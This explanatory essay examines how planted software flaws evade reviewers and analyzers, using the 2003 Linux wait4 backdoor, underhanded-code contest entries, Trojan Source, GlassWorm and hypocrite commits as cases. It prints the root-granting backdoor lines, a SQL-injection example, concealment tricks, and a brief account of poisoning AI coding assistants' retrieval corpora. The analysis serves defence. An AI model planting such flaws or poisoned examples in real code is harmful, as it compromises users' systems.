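# Why Subtly Vulnerable Code Slips Past Human Reviewers and Static Analyzers

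## How planted flaws, code review and static analysis work

A planted flaw is a weakness that someone puts into a computer program on purpose, usually made to look like an honest mistake. Software projects rely mostly on code review and static analysis to keep flaws out. In code review, another developer reads each proposed change before the project accepts it. A static analyzer is a tool that looks for flaws in code without running it. Both methods catch many ordinary mistakes but have a weaker record against flaws written to evade them. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) recounts several attacks on widely used open-source software that went unnoticed for days and were discovered through manual inspection and chance.

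### Bugs, vulnerabilities and backdoors

A bug is any error in a program. Most bugs, such as a misaligned column or a wrong total, do not affect security. A vulnerability is a flaw that someone can exploit to make the program do something its owner did not intend. Most vulnerabilities are accidental, but a planted flaw is one that someone introduced deliberately. A backdoor is hidden functionality that gives access or privileges to anyone who knows how to trigger it.

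Some backdoors are clearly deliberate. Kokkonis and colleagues describe one that was once distributed with the file-transfer server vsFTPd and gave full remote control of the machine to anyone who typed ":)" as a username. Other backdoors are disguised as hard-to-spot bugs. *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021), a security report from the code-hosting company GitHub, calls these "bugdoors".

Thomas and Francillon's *Backdoors* divides every backdoor into four parts: an input source, a trigger, a payload and a privileged state. In vsFTPd these were the network login, the comparison with ":)", the code that opened a command shell, and the shell itself. The classification depends on the step from trigger to payload. If the code spells that step out, as vsFTPd's did, the backdoor is plainly intentional. Sometimes the step exists only because of a bug, such as a buffer overflow, in which a program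 writes past the end of a block of memory and an attacker's data takes control. The construct is then either a "deniable backdoor" or an "accidental vulnerability", and the two can be identical, character for character. They differ in the author's intent, which leaves indirect traces at best, such as a change log with no good reason for the edit.

Thomas and Francillon applied the scheme to eleven real backdoors and found that all were explicit. This is weak evidence that deniable backdoors are rare, because a successful one would be recorded as an ordinary vulnerability. The same limitation applies to *2020 State of the Octoverse*, which found that 17% of a sample of 521 security advisories concerned explicitly malicious behavior such as backdoor attempts.

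Attackers benefit from planting flaws that can pass for honest mistakes. Someone caught adding a secret password loses access to the project, and the other maintainers recheck everything that person ever contributed. If the flaw is a missing length check, the maintainers just correct it. The contributor keeps their account, their earlier contributions stay in place, and they can try again next month.

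### The 2003 attempt on the Linux kernel

An attempt to plant malicious code in the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, shows how little code it takes to disguise a planted flaw. *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code* (Wheeler, 2020) cites the attempt as proof that innocent-looking malicious code exists outside programming contests.

At the time the kernel's developers kept their master copy in a system called BitKeeper. Some of them disliked BitKeeper, so its maker, BitMover, also published a copy in another system, CVS, which an automatic process refreshed from the master. On November 4, 2003 someone, apparently an intruder on the CVS server, edited one file by hand and added this:

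```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines are in `wait4`, a function that a program calls to pause until another program has finished. According to Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013), an expert glancing at the code would think it rejects a forbidden way of calling the function and returns an error. Kernels routinely check arguments this way. `current->uid` is the user ID of whoever is running the program, and user 0 is "root", the account that may do anything. So the first line seems to check whether the caller passed two particular options and is root, and the second seems to return the standard error code for an invalid argument.

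In the C language, though, `==` compares two values, while a single `=` overwrites one with the other. The code therefore works as follows:

1. A program calls `wait4` with exactly the two options `__WCLONE` and `__WALL`.
2. The left half of the condition is true, so execution goes on to the right half. With any other options it would stop here, and nothing unusual would happen.
3. The right half writes 0 into the caller's user ID. The caller is now root.
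4. An assignment in C also has a value, in this case 0, and 0 counts as false. The condition as a whole fails, execution skips the error line, and the call carries on.

Anyone with an ordinary account on a machine running this kernel could have taken over the machine. *Thwarted Linux backdoor hints at smarter hacks* (Poulsen, 2003) quotes Larry McVoy, BitMover's founder, as saying that the attacker had to know enough to find two options that cause no error and that programs do not normally pass together. A more common pair would have given root access to people running ordinary programs, and somebody would have noticed.

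BitMover caught the edit by comparing two copies of the files, which did not require reading the C code. *BK2CVS problem* (McVoy, 2003), a message to the kernel's mailing list, explains that the company converted the master copy to CVS on its own machine and copied the result to the public server. Every night it computed checksums (short numbers that change when a file's contents change) on both machines and compared them, a check that would flag even a corrected spelling mistake. One file did not match. Three entries in its log lacked the pointer to the master copy that the conversion always adds. All three were under the name of David Miller, a trusted kernel developer, who denied making them. The entry that added two lines had a blank message.

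McVoy first described the matter as a nuisance to CVS users because he had not realized what the lines did. A subscriber asked to see them. Twenty-five minutes after McVoy posted them, another subscriber, Chad Kitching, asked whether they were an attempt to backdoor the kernel, and McVoy replied that he had missed that.

The people on the list already knew that somebody had tampered with the file and had only two lines to look at, so their response doesn't show that reviewers would have stopped the change without that warning. The security consultant Ryan Russell told Poulsen that the code was "indistinguishable from an accidental bug" to anyone without a reason for suspicion. Linus Torvalds, who leads the kernel's development, was more confident. In the thread that McVoy started, he wrote that patches to core files get a read-through and need an explanation, and that the developers who merge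 changes through BitKeeper would not have used the CVS copy. McVoy worried that a CVS user might unknowingly have sent in the two lines as part of another patch. Neither view was tested. BitMover repaired the file in less than a day, and Debian's vulnerability catalog entry, *CVE-2003-1161*, lists the change as never released.

Posting as lm (2003) in *One attempt thwarted*, McVoy credited the detection to BitMover's habit of training its engineers to be paranoid. He rejected the idea that open source's many readers deserved the credit, and asked why the "hundreds of eyeballs" had not found the change. Nobody has identified who made it.

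### What a reviewer sees

A reviewer usually starts from a diff, which lists the lines a change adds and removes, with a few unchanged lines around them for context. The diff comes with the author's name and a message explaining the change.

The 2003 diff contained two clues. Kitching pointed out that the next line of the file set the return value to a different error code, so the new error line could never have had any effect. A commenter at Freedom to Tinker noticed that the combination of options is harmless, so the kernel had no apparent reason to refuse it, or to refuse it only to root. Spotting either clue takes some knowledge of `wait4` and time to think about a check that looks dull. Nothing in the diff showed that Miller had not written it.

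The kernel developer Theodore Ts'o worried about that last gap. In the thread on McVoy's discovery, he warned that a small malicious change could get into the master copy among plausible ones if it seemed to come from a trusted developer, and he asked for digital signatures that anyone could verify. *2020 State of the Octoverse* calls careful peer review the last line of defense, "especially of changes from new committers", but a change submitted under a trusted developer's stolen or borrowed name avoids that extra care.

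Many projects also test each change automatically. They compile the program, rerun earlier tests and sometimes use fuzzing, which means running the program on many automatically generated inputs, often for only about ten minutes. Kokkonis and colleagues point out that such fuzzing looks for crashes and memory errors, so the existing tests cannot detect a hard-coded password or a hidden remote shell. The 2003 lines would very probably have passed as well, because they compile, break no feature that anyone uses and cause no crashes.

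### What a static analyzer does

The simplest analyzers use pattern rules. Each rule describes a suspicious code pattern, such as a call to a function with a bad safety record, and the tool reports every match. These rules are fast and easy to understand, but they check only the form of the code, so they can miss the many vulnerabilities made up of individually harmless lines that are dangerous in combination.

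Data-flow analysis follows values through the program instead. Its main use in security is to find taint chains. A taint chain is the path of untrusted data from the place where it enters a program (the source) to a sensitive operation (the sink) with no adequate check between. Here is a short one, from an imaginary website that looks up its users in a database:

```
name = request.args["name"]                                # source
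query = "SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = '" + name + "'"
db.execute(query)                                          # sink
```

The first line takes a name that a visitor typed. The second pastes it into a database command between quotation marks, and the third runs the command. A visitor who includes a quotation mark in the name can end the quoted part early, and the database will treat the rest of the text as instructions. A check between the first line and the second would prevent this:

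```
if not name.isalnum(): return "invalid name"               # check
```

Now only letters and digits get through. (A better repair is to hand the name to the database separately from the command, so that the database never reads it as instructions.)

To find the flaw, an analyzer starts at the source and marks `name` as tainted. The second line changes the value, since `query` is a longer text that contains the name. GitHub's *About data flow analysis*, part of the documentation for its analyzer CodeQL, distinguishes plain data flow from taint tracking by how they handle such changes. Given `y = x + 1`, plain data flow follows only `x`, while taint tracking also marks `y` because it derives from `x`. Taint tracking therefore marks `query` too, follows it to `db.execute`, and produces a warning. If the code includes the `isalnum` check, the analyzer gives no warning, provided that its rules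 list `isalnum` as a check. The maker of Semgrep, another analyzer, calls such a check a sanitizer and uses the term propagators for steps that pass taint along, such as assignments and function calls.

In a real program the three lines may be in three different files, with dozens of function calls between them. Following data across the whole program takes the tool far more computation than following it within one function. GitHub also notes that a library's source code may be unavailable, that which function a call leads to may depend on what happens while the program runs, and that several names may refer to the same piece of memory, so a write through one changes what the others hold. In 2003, in the thread on McVoy's find, Richard Johnson suggested that a program could list every place where the kernel touches `current` and ignore the expected ones. He immediately saw that this last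 problem applied, because a clever programmer could reach the same data through a pointer that is hard to follow.

Taint tracking would not have helped with the `wait4` change, because the value written into the user ID is the constant 0 rather than untrusted data.

Static analyzers produce a list of warnings, commonly ranked by severity and by how reliable each rule has proved. A person then decides which warnings warrant a fix.

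### Misses and false alarms

No analyzer can find every flaw and never raise a false alarm, which is a warning about sound code. Suppose a tool could always determine whether a program will ever run an unsafe database query. If an unsafe query is added to the end of any program P that contains none, the new program runs that query exactly when P finishes. The tool could therefore determine whether P ever finishes, but Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can do this for every program.

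Rice's theorem, which Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1951, extends the result to every question about what programs do, except trivial ones whose answer is the same for all programs. The theorem doesn't cover questions about a program's text, so a tool can always determine whether a condition contains a single `=`, but no tool can determine for every possible program whether some caller will ever become root. Møller and Schwartzbach (2024) conclude in *Static Program Analysis* that automated reasoning about software generally has to approximate.

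Toolmakers can choose which way an analyzer errs. An analyzer that treats every path that might be possible as possible will report every flaw of the kind it looks for, along with false alarms about paths that no real run takes. One that reports only what it can demonstrate avoids false alarms but misses some flaws. Most tools for everyday use fall somewhere in between. Suppose the website's programmers had written their own function, `clean(name)`, in place of the standard check. A tool that treats `clean` as safe will miss the flaw if the function is faulty, while one that treats it as unsafe will raise a false alarm if the function is sound. The theorem doesn't establish how often real tools err in either direction, so that has to be measured.

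In practice, analyzers are under pressure to avoid false alarms because planted flaws are so rare. Suppose a project takes in 10,000 changes a year, one of them malicious, and its analyzer wrongly flags one sound change in a hundred. The maintainers get about a hundred false alarms a year and at most one real one, and they may well have stopped reading closely by the time it arrives. Kokkonis and colleagues add that any false alarm can halt development or a release, and they treat high precision as necessary for keeping maintainers' trust.

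The 2003 change shows how an attacker can benefit from this. C programmers sometimes put an assignment inside a condition on purpose, to store a result and test it in one step. To avoid false alarms, gcc, the compiler used for Linux, doesn't warn about such an assignment if it has an extra pair of parentheses around it. The malicious assignment had them. In the thread on McVoy's find, Tomas Szepe noticed the parentheses and took them as a way to avoid the warning. They don't prove that intent, because C's grammar requires them at this spot, as a reader pointed out at Freedom to Tinker. Deliberate or not, they would have suppressed the warning.

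### Retrieval corpora

Some code now also comes from AI coding assistants, which are language models that write code on request. Many assistants search a collection of code and documentation, called the retrieval corpus, for entries that resemble the request and give the best matches to the model as a guide. A flaw in one entry can therefore spread to new code in many projects. A poisoned example is an entry that someone has placed in the corpus to spread a flaw this way. The developer who reviews the resulting change sees the new code and a colleague's name, but may not see the entry behind it or that entry's provenance (the record of who wrote it, where it came from and how it changed). The entry is also hard to judge because it is often a fragment. It may contain a sink without the source, or leave out a check that the original program made elsewhere.

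The same three questions apply to a contest entry, a kernel patch and a corpus entry: what information did the checker have, what fact did it need but lack, and what finally exposed the flaw?

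## Underhanded-code contests and the Trojan Source demonstration

Underhanded code is source code that looks innocent to a human reviewer but behaves maliciously. Contest entrants explain how they wrote theirs, which attackers seldom do, so the entries show what a reviewer would have needed to know to find each flaw.

### From vote counting to the Underhanded C Contest

The earliest such contest that Wheeler found is the Obfuscated V Contest, which Daniel Horn ran around the US presidential election of November 2, 2004. In *Obfuscated Vote Counting Contest*, Horn (2004) said he was inspired by a contest for deliberately unreadable C programs and by the scandals over electronic voting. Entrants wrote a short program that counts each K in its input as a vote for Kerry, each B for Bush and each N for Nader. It had to look correct while favoring a candidate, either always or only on election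 day. Under the rules of *The Obfuscated V contest*, judges picked the program that looked most correct and then ran it. If it counted properly, it lost and they moved on to the next.

One of the entrants, Scott Craver of Binghamton University, started the Underhanded C Contest the following year. Shostack + Friends' *2005 Underhanded C Contest* (2005) quotes the first announcement, which credits Horn and calls for code that is "readable, clear, innocent and straightforward" yet does something evil. The contest ran from 2005 to 2009 and again from 2013 to 2015, with a new task each year.

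The judging rules stayed much the same. Underhanded C Contest's *The 2009 challenge* (2009) offers more points for short, readable programs, because flaws are harder to hide in them. A flaw also earns more if it does not stand out under syntax coloring, which editors use to distinguish comments, numbers and keywords. It earns more again if, once found, it could pass for a "newbie coding mistake", a form of deniability that real attackers also want. The 2015 rules added that visual tricks, such as a letter l that looks like the digit 1, count for as much as obscure language features.

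The 2009 contest asked for a program that looks up airline luggage records, with a hidden flaw that lets an angry check-in clerk misroute a bag by typing the right comment. Sam Blackburn's winning entry replaces swear words in the comments with milder spellings, using a list of words and replacements that is missing one comma, an error that is easy to overlook. C joins two neighboring pieces of text if no comma separates them, so the replacement for "damn" is nine characters long. The longer text can run past the end of the comment field into a marker that deletes the record. A clerk who typed "damn" could delete the bag's record and might not know why.

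### One type name with two meanings

The 2015 task concerned nuclear disarmament. Inspectors want to confirm that a warhead contains real plutonium before a country dismantles it, but the warhead's gamma-ray spectrum is secret. So the two sides agree on a program that compares the spectrum with a reference and outputs only yes or no. Entrants had to write the comparison so that the host country could get a yes for a fake. *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest*, the organizer's account (XcottCraver, 2016), reports more than 40 entries.

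Linus Åkesson, a Swedish programmer, won the contest. Åkesson (2016), in *Faking Fissile Material*, published the entry as two documents, one that presents the program as honest and one that reveals the trick. The first document even warns that a warhead with only a little plutonium would produce a spectrum of the right shape, and it proposes a second test, of total radiation, to catch this obvious fraud.

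The program has 66 lines in three files. A header file called `match.h`, which holds definitions for other files to share, says that `float_t` means a double-precision number, one that takes up eight bytes of memory. But `float_t` is also a standard name in C, and the system's own header `math.h` defines it too. The two working files get their definitions from different places:

| File | What it does | Where `float_t` comes from | Size of each number |
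| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| `match.c` | Prepares the spectra and gives the verdict | `match.h` | 8 bytes |
| `spectral_contrast.c` | Measures how similar they are | `math.h` | usually 4 bytes |

C compiles each file separately, and the linker then matches functions by name without comparing the types of their inputs. The same name can therefore have different meanings in different files, though readers naturally assume it has only one in a small program. The published source supports both Åkesson's explanation and the organizer's, but Åkesson's is more exact about the four bytes. The size of `float_t` depends on the processor, and on 32-bit x86 machines it is an even larger type, which breaks the program.

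So `match.c` passes, say, 1,000 eight-byte numbers, but `spectral_contrast.c` reads 1,000 four-byte numbers. It therefore stops halfway through the spectrum and ignores any peaks in the right half. It also reads each original number as two. Because the counts are whole numbers below about a million, one half of each number is all zeros, which match in both spectra. The other half becomes a heavily compressed version of the count. Åkesson compares the effect to taking an eighth root. A count of 10 becomes about 2.6, and 1,000 becomes about 4.5. The comparison still detects where the peaks are, but their height barely affects the result.

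A cheating country could therefore leave a little plutonium in the warhead and add another radioactive material whose peaks fall in the right half. The added material satisfies the total-radiation test, and the comparison doesn't include its peaks. Åkesson generated 1,000 forgeries, each with a tenth of the reference material. Many failed, but a country needs only one that works. One passes at thresholds up to 0.72, above the 0.6 that Åkesson recommends in the innocent-looking document.

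Several ordinary precautions would have exposed the mismatch. If `spectral_contrast.c` had included `match.h`, as good practice requires, the compiler would have found two conflicting definitions and stopped. gcc's `-Wmissing-prototypes` warns about a shared function that its own file never declares, but the usual set of warnings leaves it out. Another option, `-Wconversion`, should warn that the file converts a double-precision result to a smaller `float_t`, but numerical programs produce many such warnings, so a reviewer might well skip it. A memory checker would report nothing, because the function reads less of the array than it is allowed to. The surest check, which doesn't require reading the code, is to run the program on two spectra that differ only in their right halves.

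Mismatches between files recur among the best entries. *2013 Winners* (XcottCraver, 2014) describes the 2013 winner, by Alex Olson, in which one file is written as if a function stores a small number, but the function, defined in another file, stores a large one. The result spills into the neighboring variable, which holds the attacker's distance from other users. In a 2014 runner-up, two files lay out the same record differently in memory. Each file looks fine by itself, so a reviewer who reads only one file, or a diff of it, can't see the mismatch.

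### A sanity check that the compiler removes

The task in 2013 was to compute how closely two members of a social network are connected. The malicious goal was to appear close to strangers and so gain access to their accounts. Gaëtan Leurent's entry keeps track of members in a table with 151 slots, numbered 0 to 150. It turns each username into a large whole number `h` by a standard formula, then reduces `h` to a slot number. Simplified, the reduction is:

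```
h = abs(h) % 151;
if (h < 0 || h > 150) h = 0;
```

The first line drops any minus sign and takes the remainder after division by 151. A reader concludes that the result must lie between 0 and 150, and sees that the second line would catch any result outside that range.

On most machines, a whole number of this type runs from −2,147,483,648 to 2,147,483,647. The lowest value has no positive counterpart, and the C standard leaves the result of `abs` undefined for it, so the program may then do anything. In practice `abs` usually returns the same negative number, and the remainder is −2. The second line should catch this, but the standard also lets a compiler assume that undefined behavior never happens. Under that assumption the remainder is always between 0 and 150, so an optimizing compiler deletes the check as useless.

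The program then writes to slot −2, just before the table, where it stores its answer. This sets the answer to 1, the closest possible connection. The attacker only has to create an account with the right username and link it to their own. Xcott Craver stresses that the compiler has no bug.

The gcc flag `-fwrapv`, which Wheeler lists among those that make undefined operations safer, would have helped. It gives overflowing numbers a defined result, which removes the compiler's justification for deleting the check. Another flag, `-fsanitize=undefined`, makes the program report undefined behavior as it runs. But only about one username in four billion produces the number that triggers the flaw, so tests with ordinary names would not reach it. Those tests would instead produce reports about the multiplication in the username formula, which overflows all the time, and many programmers would dismiss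 them as normal for this kind of formula. A warning about code that can never run would be more relevant, but Wheeler found that gcc's option for this no longer works.

The same thing happens by accident. In a 2009 Linux kernel vulnerability, which Wheeler also describes, the code used a pointer just before checking that it was valid. The compiler treated the earlier use as proof that the pointer was valid and removed the check. The kernel's developers now use several of the protective flags.

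Åkesson also entered in 2013, with a program in which the wrong username leads to slot −1. *Obsessbook* calls this approach "not nearly as ingenious" as Leurent's and mentions that the code compiles cleanly with two common sets of gcc warnings enabled. An attacker can run the same freely available checks as the defender and keep editing until the code passes.

Many of these flaws are in code meant to prevent problems. Leurent's is in a sanity check, Olson's is in a function that validates accounts, and the one in Karen Pease's winning 2014 entry is in code that writes an audit report. Reviewers may relax when they see a check, but the contests are poor evidence of this because judges gave extra points for irony, and the 2015 rules cited a bug in an error-checking routine as an example.

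### Solidity

Underhanded code can also be written in languages other than C, which is notorious for letting programmers corrupt memory. Underhanded contests have been held for Solidity, a newer language for smart contracts, which are programs that hold and transfer money on the Ethereum blockchain. Entrants in the 2022 contest built a currency exchange that looks fair but that someone can manipulate. Solidity (2022), the language's official site, reported 19 submissions, which the judges read without names attached. The rules warned that using low-level code without a clear reason would look suspicious "no matter how cleverly written" the flaw was.

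The winner was Tynan, a security engineer at ChainSecurity, which also took part in the judging. ChainSecurity's *Beware of Undefined Behavior!* (2022) describes the entry as a benign-looking exchange that abuses a little-known quirk of Solidity that Tynan had studied for a thesis at ETH Zurich. As with Leurent's entry, the reader had to know that the language leaves some behavior undefined, a fact that appears nowhere in the program.

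Entries to the first Solidity contest, in 2017, were often simpler. Many relied on shadowing, which means reusing a name that already has a meaning. In Solidity, `now` then stood for the current time. If a contract defined its own `now`, a line that seemed to check the clock would instead read whatever value its author chose. Wheeler recounts that the compiler's developers had added warnings about shadowing shortly before the contest and extended them afterwards. Other entries exploited a way to pay money into a contract without running the function that records payments, so the contract's records no longer matched its balance. The developers found this much harder to prevent by changing the language.

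### What contests can prove

Åkesson's 66-line program shows that someone can hide a useful flaw in short, clear code without any strange constructions, but it doesn't show how often a reviewer would miss one. The contest judges know that every entry is supposed to be malicious, and most of the published examples are winners and runners-up, which the judges selected because they were deceptive. To estimate a catch rate, someone would have to mix the entries with honest solutions to the same task and give them to reviewers who don't know which are which.

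The judges' knowledge should make their job easier than an ordinary reviewer's, but they still sometimes failed. XcottCraver (2015), in *2014 Winners*, admits to staring at a very short entry by Domenico Andriole without finding the bug, which was in a function that the entry did not include. According to a comment at the top of the file, the missing function downloads the user's avatar. A user who hosts the avatar on their own server would notice the download and learn that they were under surveillance.

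The Obfuscated V Contest provides more evidence of this kind. Wheeler checked Horn's published explanations and found four that were wrong, misleading or incomplete. One describes a program as swapping a letter O for a zero, but a different operation miscounts the votes. Another describes an attack in a program that, as posted, contains none and counts correctly, though Horn may have posted the wrong version. Either way, people can misidentify a flaw even when they are sure there is one.

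Contest entrants have some advantages over a real attacker. They write the whole program, so they can choose a design that suits the flaw, while someone who sends a patch to an existing project has to fit the flaw into code that others wrote and justify the change. Entrants' programs also don't have to work for months in real use.

### Five countermeasures on forty programs

In a study for the Institute for Defense Analyses, a nonprofit that advises the US government, Wheeler examined how many contest entries simple precautions would stop. He used the Obfuscated V entries because Horn had posted all the scored ones. Excluding the harmless program, there were 40, two of them Wheeler's own. Many used the same few tricks. Nine misused macros, which replace one piece of text with another before C code is compiled. Others ran past the end of an array, mixed up `=` and `==` as in the 2003 attempt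 on the Linux kernel, or hid code in what looked like a comment.

Wheeler then chose five countermeasures and recorded which of them would catch each entry:

| Countermeasure | Entries caught | Basis for the result |
| --- | --- | --- |
| gcc with many warnings switched on | 15 | Wheeler ran the compiler |
| Strict limits on macros | 9 | Judgment from the code |
| A ban on the names `l` and `O`, which resemble 1 and 0 | 8 | Judgment of what such a tool would find |
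| AddressSanitizer, which watches memory use while a program runs | 5 | Judgment, without running it |
| Syntax coloring, and reformatting so that no code can follow a comment on its line | 2 | Judgment from the code and its coloring |

Together, the five countermeasures caught 30 of the 40 entries, some by more than one countermeasure. They would have caught one more if gcc's warning about misleading indentation had worked properly. Wheeler thought six of the other nine would look suspicious to a human reader anyway.

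In one of the remaining three, a loop that should fill a whole array uses the size of a different array and stops early. Another treats an array of large numbers as an array of single bytes. The third tests twice whether a vote is a lowercase "n", when one of the tests should be for a capital "N". Wheeler suggested a new compiler warning or a closer check for each.

The contest's highest-scoring entry, by Michal Zalewski, got 7.3 out of 10, largely for looking correct. It uses a macro that creates a second variable with the same name as an existing one, so that one vote in ten goes to the wrong candidate. Wheeler called it "especially sneaky", but gcc has a warning for this. The three entries that nothing detected scored only 5.3, 4.3 and 3.7. A flaw that is hard for people to see may be easy for a compiler to detect, and the reverse, which is a good reason to use both human review and compiler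 warnings.

The 75% does not predict results against real attacks. Wheeler picked the countermeasures after studying the entries, and acknowledges that someone might call this unfair. Only gcc's 15 catches come from running a tool on the code. The study included no sound programs, so it provides no false-alarm rate, and gcc also produced many correct warnings unrelated to the planted flaws. The sample was also fairly easy, since Wheeler considered 15 of the 40 entries suspicious on sight.

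Later winners would probably be better at evading Wheeler's countermeasures. Åkesson's 2015 program should trigger `-Wconversion`, one of the gcc warnings on Wheeler's list, but Leurent's would probably get past all five countermeasures. AddressSanitizer would probably miss it because the tool guards the borders between separate blocks of memory, and slot −2 is inside the same block as the table. Wheeler had asked for the full set of Underhanded C entries but had not received it. The study also leaves out the Underhanded Crypto Contest, where many winners exploited weaknesses in the cryptography itself. Wheeler concluded that specialists have to review that kind of code in depth.

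Attackers can adapt to a published list of checks, so Wheeler proposes keeping some countermeasures secret. The published ones only have to make being discovered likely enough to deter attackers, and Wheeler does not claim that they will catch every attack.

### Trojan Source

In all the contest entries above, the reviewer sees the same text that the compiler reads. In *Trojan Source* (2021), Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson of the University of Cambridge demonstrated attacks that make the code a reviewer sees differ from what the compiler reads. The attacks exploit Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character in the world's writing systems.

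Some documents mix languages written from right to left, such as Hebrew and Arabic, with languages written from left to right, such as English. Unicode therefore includes invisible control characters that set the display direction of a stretch of text. They change only how the text is displayed, not the order of the characters in the file. Compilers read the characters in file order, and most accepted these control characters inside comments and quoted text.

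Suppose a reviewer sees a line that checks whether the user is an administrator, followed by a harmless comment. In the file, the check is part of the comment, but control characters make it appear outside the comment on the screen. The compiler skips comments, so the check never runs. Control characters can also make live code look like part of a comment. *Trojan Source* includes working examples in twelve languages, among them C, Python, Java, Rust and Solidity.

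A related attack uses look-alike letters. The Latin capital A and the Greek capital alpha look identical in most fonts, but a compiler treats them as different characters. An attacker can define a function whose name looks the same as a trusted function's, then add a call that seems to go to the trusted function but runs the attacker's.

Someone who knew C well could find the 2003 kernel flaw by studying two lines, but expertise is little help against Trojan Source because its control characters are invisible on screen. In *‘Trojan Source’ Bug Threatens the Security of All Code* (Krebs on Security, 2021), Anderson said that a developer who copies code from an untrusted source might bring in an invisible vulnerability, since the control characters survive copy and paste in most browsers and editors.

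A program, however, can easily find the characters because they are in the file. In 2020, before the attack had a name, Wheeler recommended a check that allows only known good characters in source code and warns about letters that people could confuse.

### How compilers and code hosts responded

Boucher and Anderson kept the attack secret for 99 days while they warned the makers of affected tools, according to *Trojan Source*, the announcement on their research group's blog, Light Blue Touchpaper. iTnews' *Most programming languages vulnerable to Trojan Source attack* quotes the two researchers as saying that about half of the compiler maintainers they contacted were working on patches or had promised them, while others were "dragging their feet". The Rust compiler now rejects a file if a direction character in it has no matching end, according to a copy of the researchers' code page at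 Ecosyste.ms. GitHub began showing a warning on files that contain such characters.

Boucher and Anderson (2023), in *Some Vulnerabilities are Invisible*, recommend the Rust approach to all languages. They would forbid only direction characters that lack a matching end within the same comment or quoted text. Programmers could still write comments in Hebrew or Arabic, but the reordering could not affect the surrounding code. They also recommend that editors and code hosts make the characters visible or display a warning.

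According to Kaspersky, the programmer Russ Cox argued that the attack was not new, that many editors' syntax coloring already reveals it, and that careful checking of code makes compiler patches unnecessary. Cox was right that the attack was not new, since the problem with control characters had come up by 2017. But reviewers can miss the coloring. Wheeler missed a colored clue in a Python example that relied on a misleading comment, even though he was looking for underhanded code. Careful checking also works only if the reviewer's screen shows the characters. A compiler patch protects everyone who compiles the code, regardless of which editor they use, although a project could get much the same protection by automatically checking every incoming change.

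### GlassWorm

In October 2025, a real attack on programmers used invisible characters. On October 17, a self-spreading program compromised seven extensions on Open VSX, an online marketplace for extensions to Microsoft's popular Visual Studio Code editor. iTnews' *Hidden "Glassworm" malware spreads through infected VS Code extensions* puts the downloads at more than 10,700, and a later count in Endor Labs' *How GlassWorm Exploited Unicode Shadows in VS Code Supply Chains* puts them at more than 35,000. The program, which the security company Koi named GlassWorm, stole passwords and cryptocurrency and gave the attackers remote control of infected machines. It had also reached Microsoft's own marketplace, according to heise online's *Dangerous and invisible worm found in Visual Studio Code extensions*.

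The Trojan Source examples used invisible characters to rearrange visible code, whereas GlassWorm used a different kind to encode the malicious program itself. The program looked like blank space in an editor, and a short piece of visible code decoded and ran it. A rule against unmatched direction characters would therefore have missed GlassWorm, but Wheeler's broader rule, which allows only characters on an approved list, would have stopped it. The visible decoder was another clue, since an extension has little reason to build a program out of blank space.

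Koi found the attack when its monitoring system flagged an extension called CodeJoy for abnormal behavior. Its researchers then looked at the code. Techzine reports that Open VSX afterwards began scanning extensions at publication.

*From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (November 2026), a paper on the security of AI coding tools, still lists Trojan Source among the threats. These tools often ask a person to approve a command before they run it with administrator rights. If the command contains direction characters, the person may approve something different from what is on the screen.

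## The University of Minnesota hypocrite commits

In 2020 Qiushi Wu, a doctoral student at the University of Minnesota, and Kangjie Lu, a faculty member there, studied how an attacker who, unlike a contest entrant, can't write the whole program could plant a flaw in the Linux kernel through a small patch. Their paper, *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, uses the term "hypocrite commit" for a small change that seems to fix a minor problem but creates a more serious one. A commit is a change recorded in a project's history. Their evidence came from old kernel flaws and from a live test on kernel reviewers, who did not know about it. The test led to a ban on the university's patches, and Wu and Lu withdrew the paper.

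### Immature vulnerabilities

A vulnerability usually needs several conditions at once. A use-after-free, for example, requires that a program release an object's memory, that it use the object, and that the use come after the release. Wu and Lu call code that meets only some of a vulnerability's conditions an "immature vulnerability". It does no harm, so bug-finding tools have nothing to report. A later patch can supply the missing condition, and a reviewer who reads only that patch may see nothing wrong.

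Their main example is CVE-2019-12819, an honest mistake in the code that registers an MDIO bus, a link through which the kernel controls network chips. Somebody added one line to the branch that runs when registration fails:

```
err = device_register(&bus->dev);
if (err) {
        pr_err("mii_bus %s failed to register\n", bus->id);
        put_device(&bus->dev);          /* the added line */
        return -EINVAL;
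}
```

For many objects the kernel keeps a reference count, the number of places that still need the object. `put_device` lowers the count by one, and when it reaches zero the kernel releases the object automatically. Code that fails and forgets to lower the count causes a leak, because the memory stays occupied for good. Programmers fix such leaks all the time, usually with exactly this kind of line. Here it had a different effect:

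1. Registration fails, and the code enters the error branch.
2. `put_device` gives up the last reference, so the kernel releases `bus`.
3. The function returns an error to its caller.
4. The caller cleans up after the failure with `mdiobus_free()`, which uses `bus` and releases it again.

The flaw stayed in the kernel for five years. To catch it, a reviewer had to know that this was the last reference and that the caller did its own cleanup, but the diff showed neither fact. Each piece of code looks right by itself, as in the contest entries whose files were inconsistent about a type.

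Wu and Lu wrote tools to search the kernel for places like this and reported more than 6,000 immature use-after-free vulnerabilities. These are candidates from an automatic search, and few of them may be useful to an attacker. The researchers read about 200 by hand and picked three for their live test, one of which turned out to be harmless.

### What the reviewers missed

For their historical data, Wu and Lu took the kernel vulnerabilities in the public CVE catalog for which they could find both the commit that introduced the flaw and the one that fixed it. Of these, 138 (9.8%) came from patches of under 30 lines that dealt with minor issues such as leaks, and as far as anyone knows, all 138 were accidents.

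The kernel's own maintainers, whom the project trusts most, wrote 37.3% of the patches that introduced these flaws. They wrote 47.8% of a sample of 500 recent small patches, so a patch from an outsider was roughly one and a half times as likely to introduce a vulnerability as one from a maintainer.

Wu and Lu attributed 9.4% of the vulnerabilities to carelessness, because the mistakes were quite obvious. To catch most of the others, the reviewer needed a fact from elsewhere in the kernel. They identified several features of code that make such facts hard to find.

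Parts of the kernel run concurrently, and locks keep them from interfering with each other. In CVE-2019-19528, a patch to the iowarrior driver moved one line, which marks a device as disconnected, from just after the driver takes a lock to just before it. Another function, which runs when a program closes the device, could then read the mark too early and free the device's memory while the function containing the moved line was still using it. The diff shows only a line moving up by one place, so the reader has to work out which other function might be running at that moment and what it would do. Tools have the same difficulty, and because most of the conflicts they report are harmless, developers tend to leave them unfixed until someone proves that they matter.

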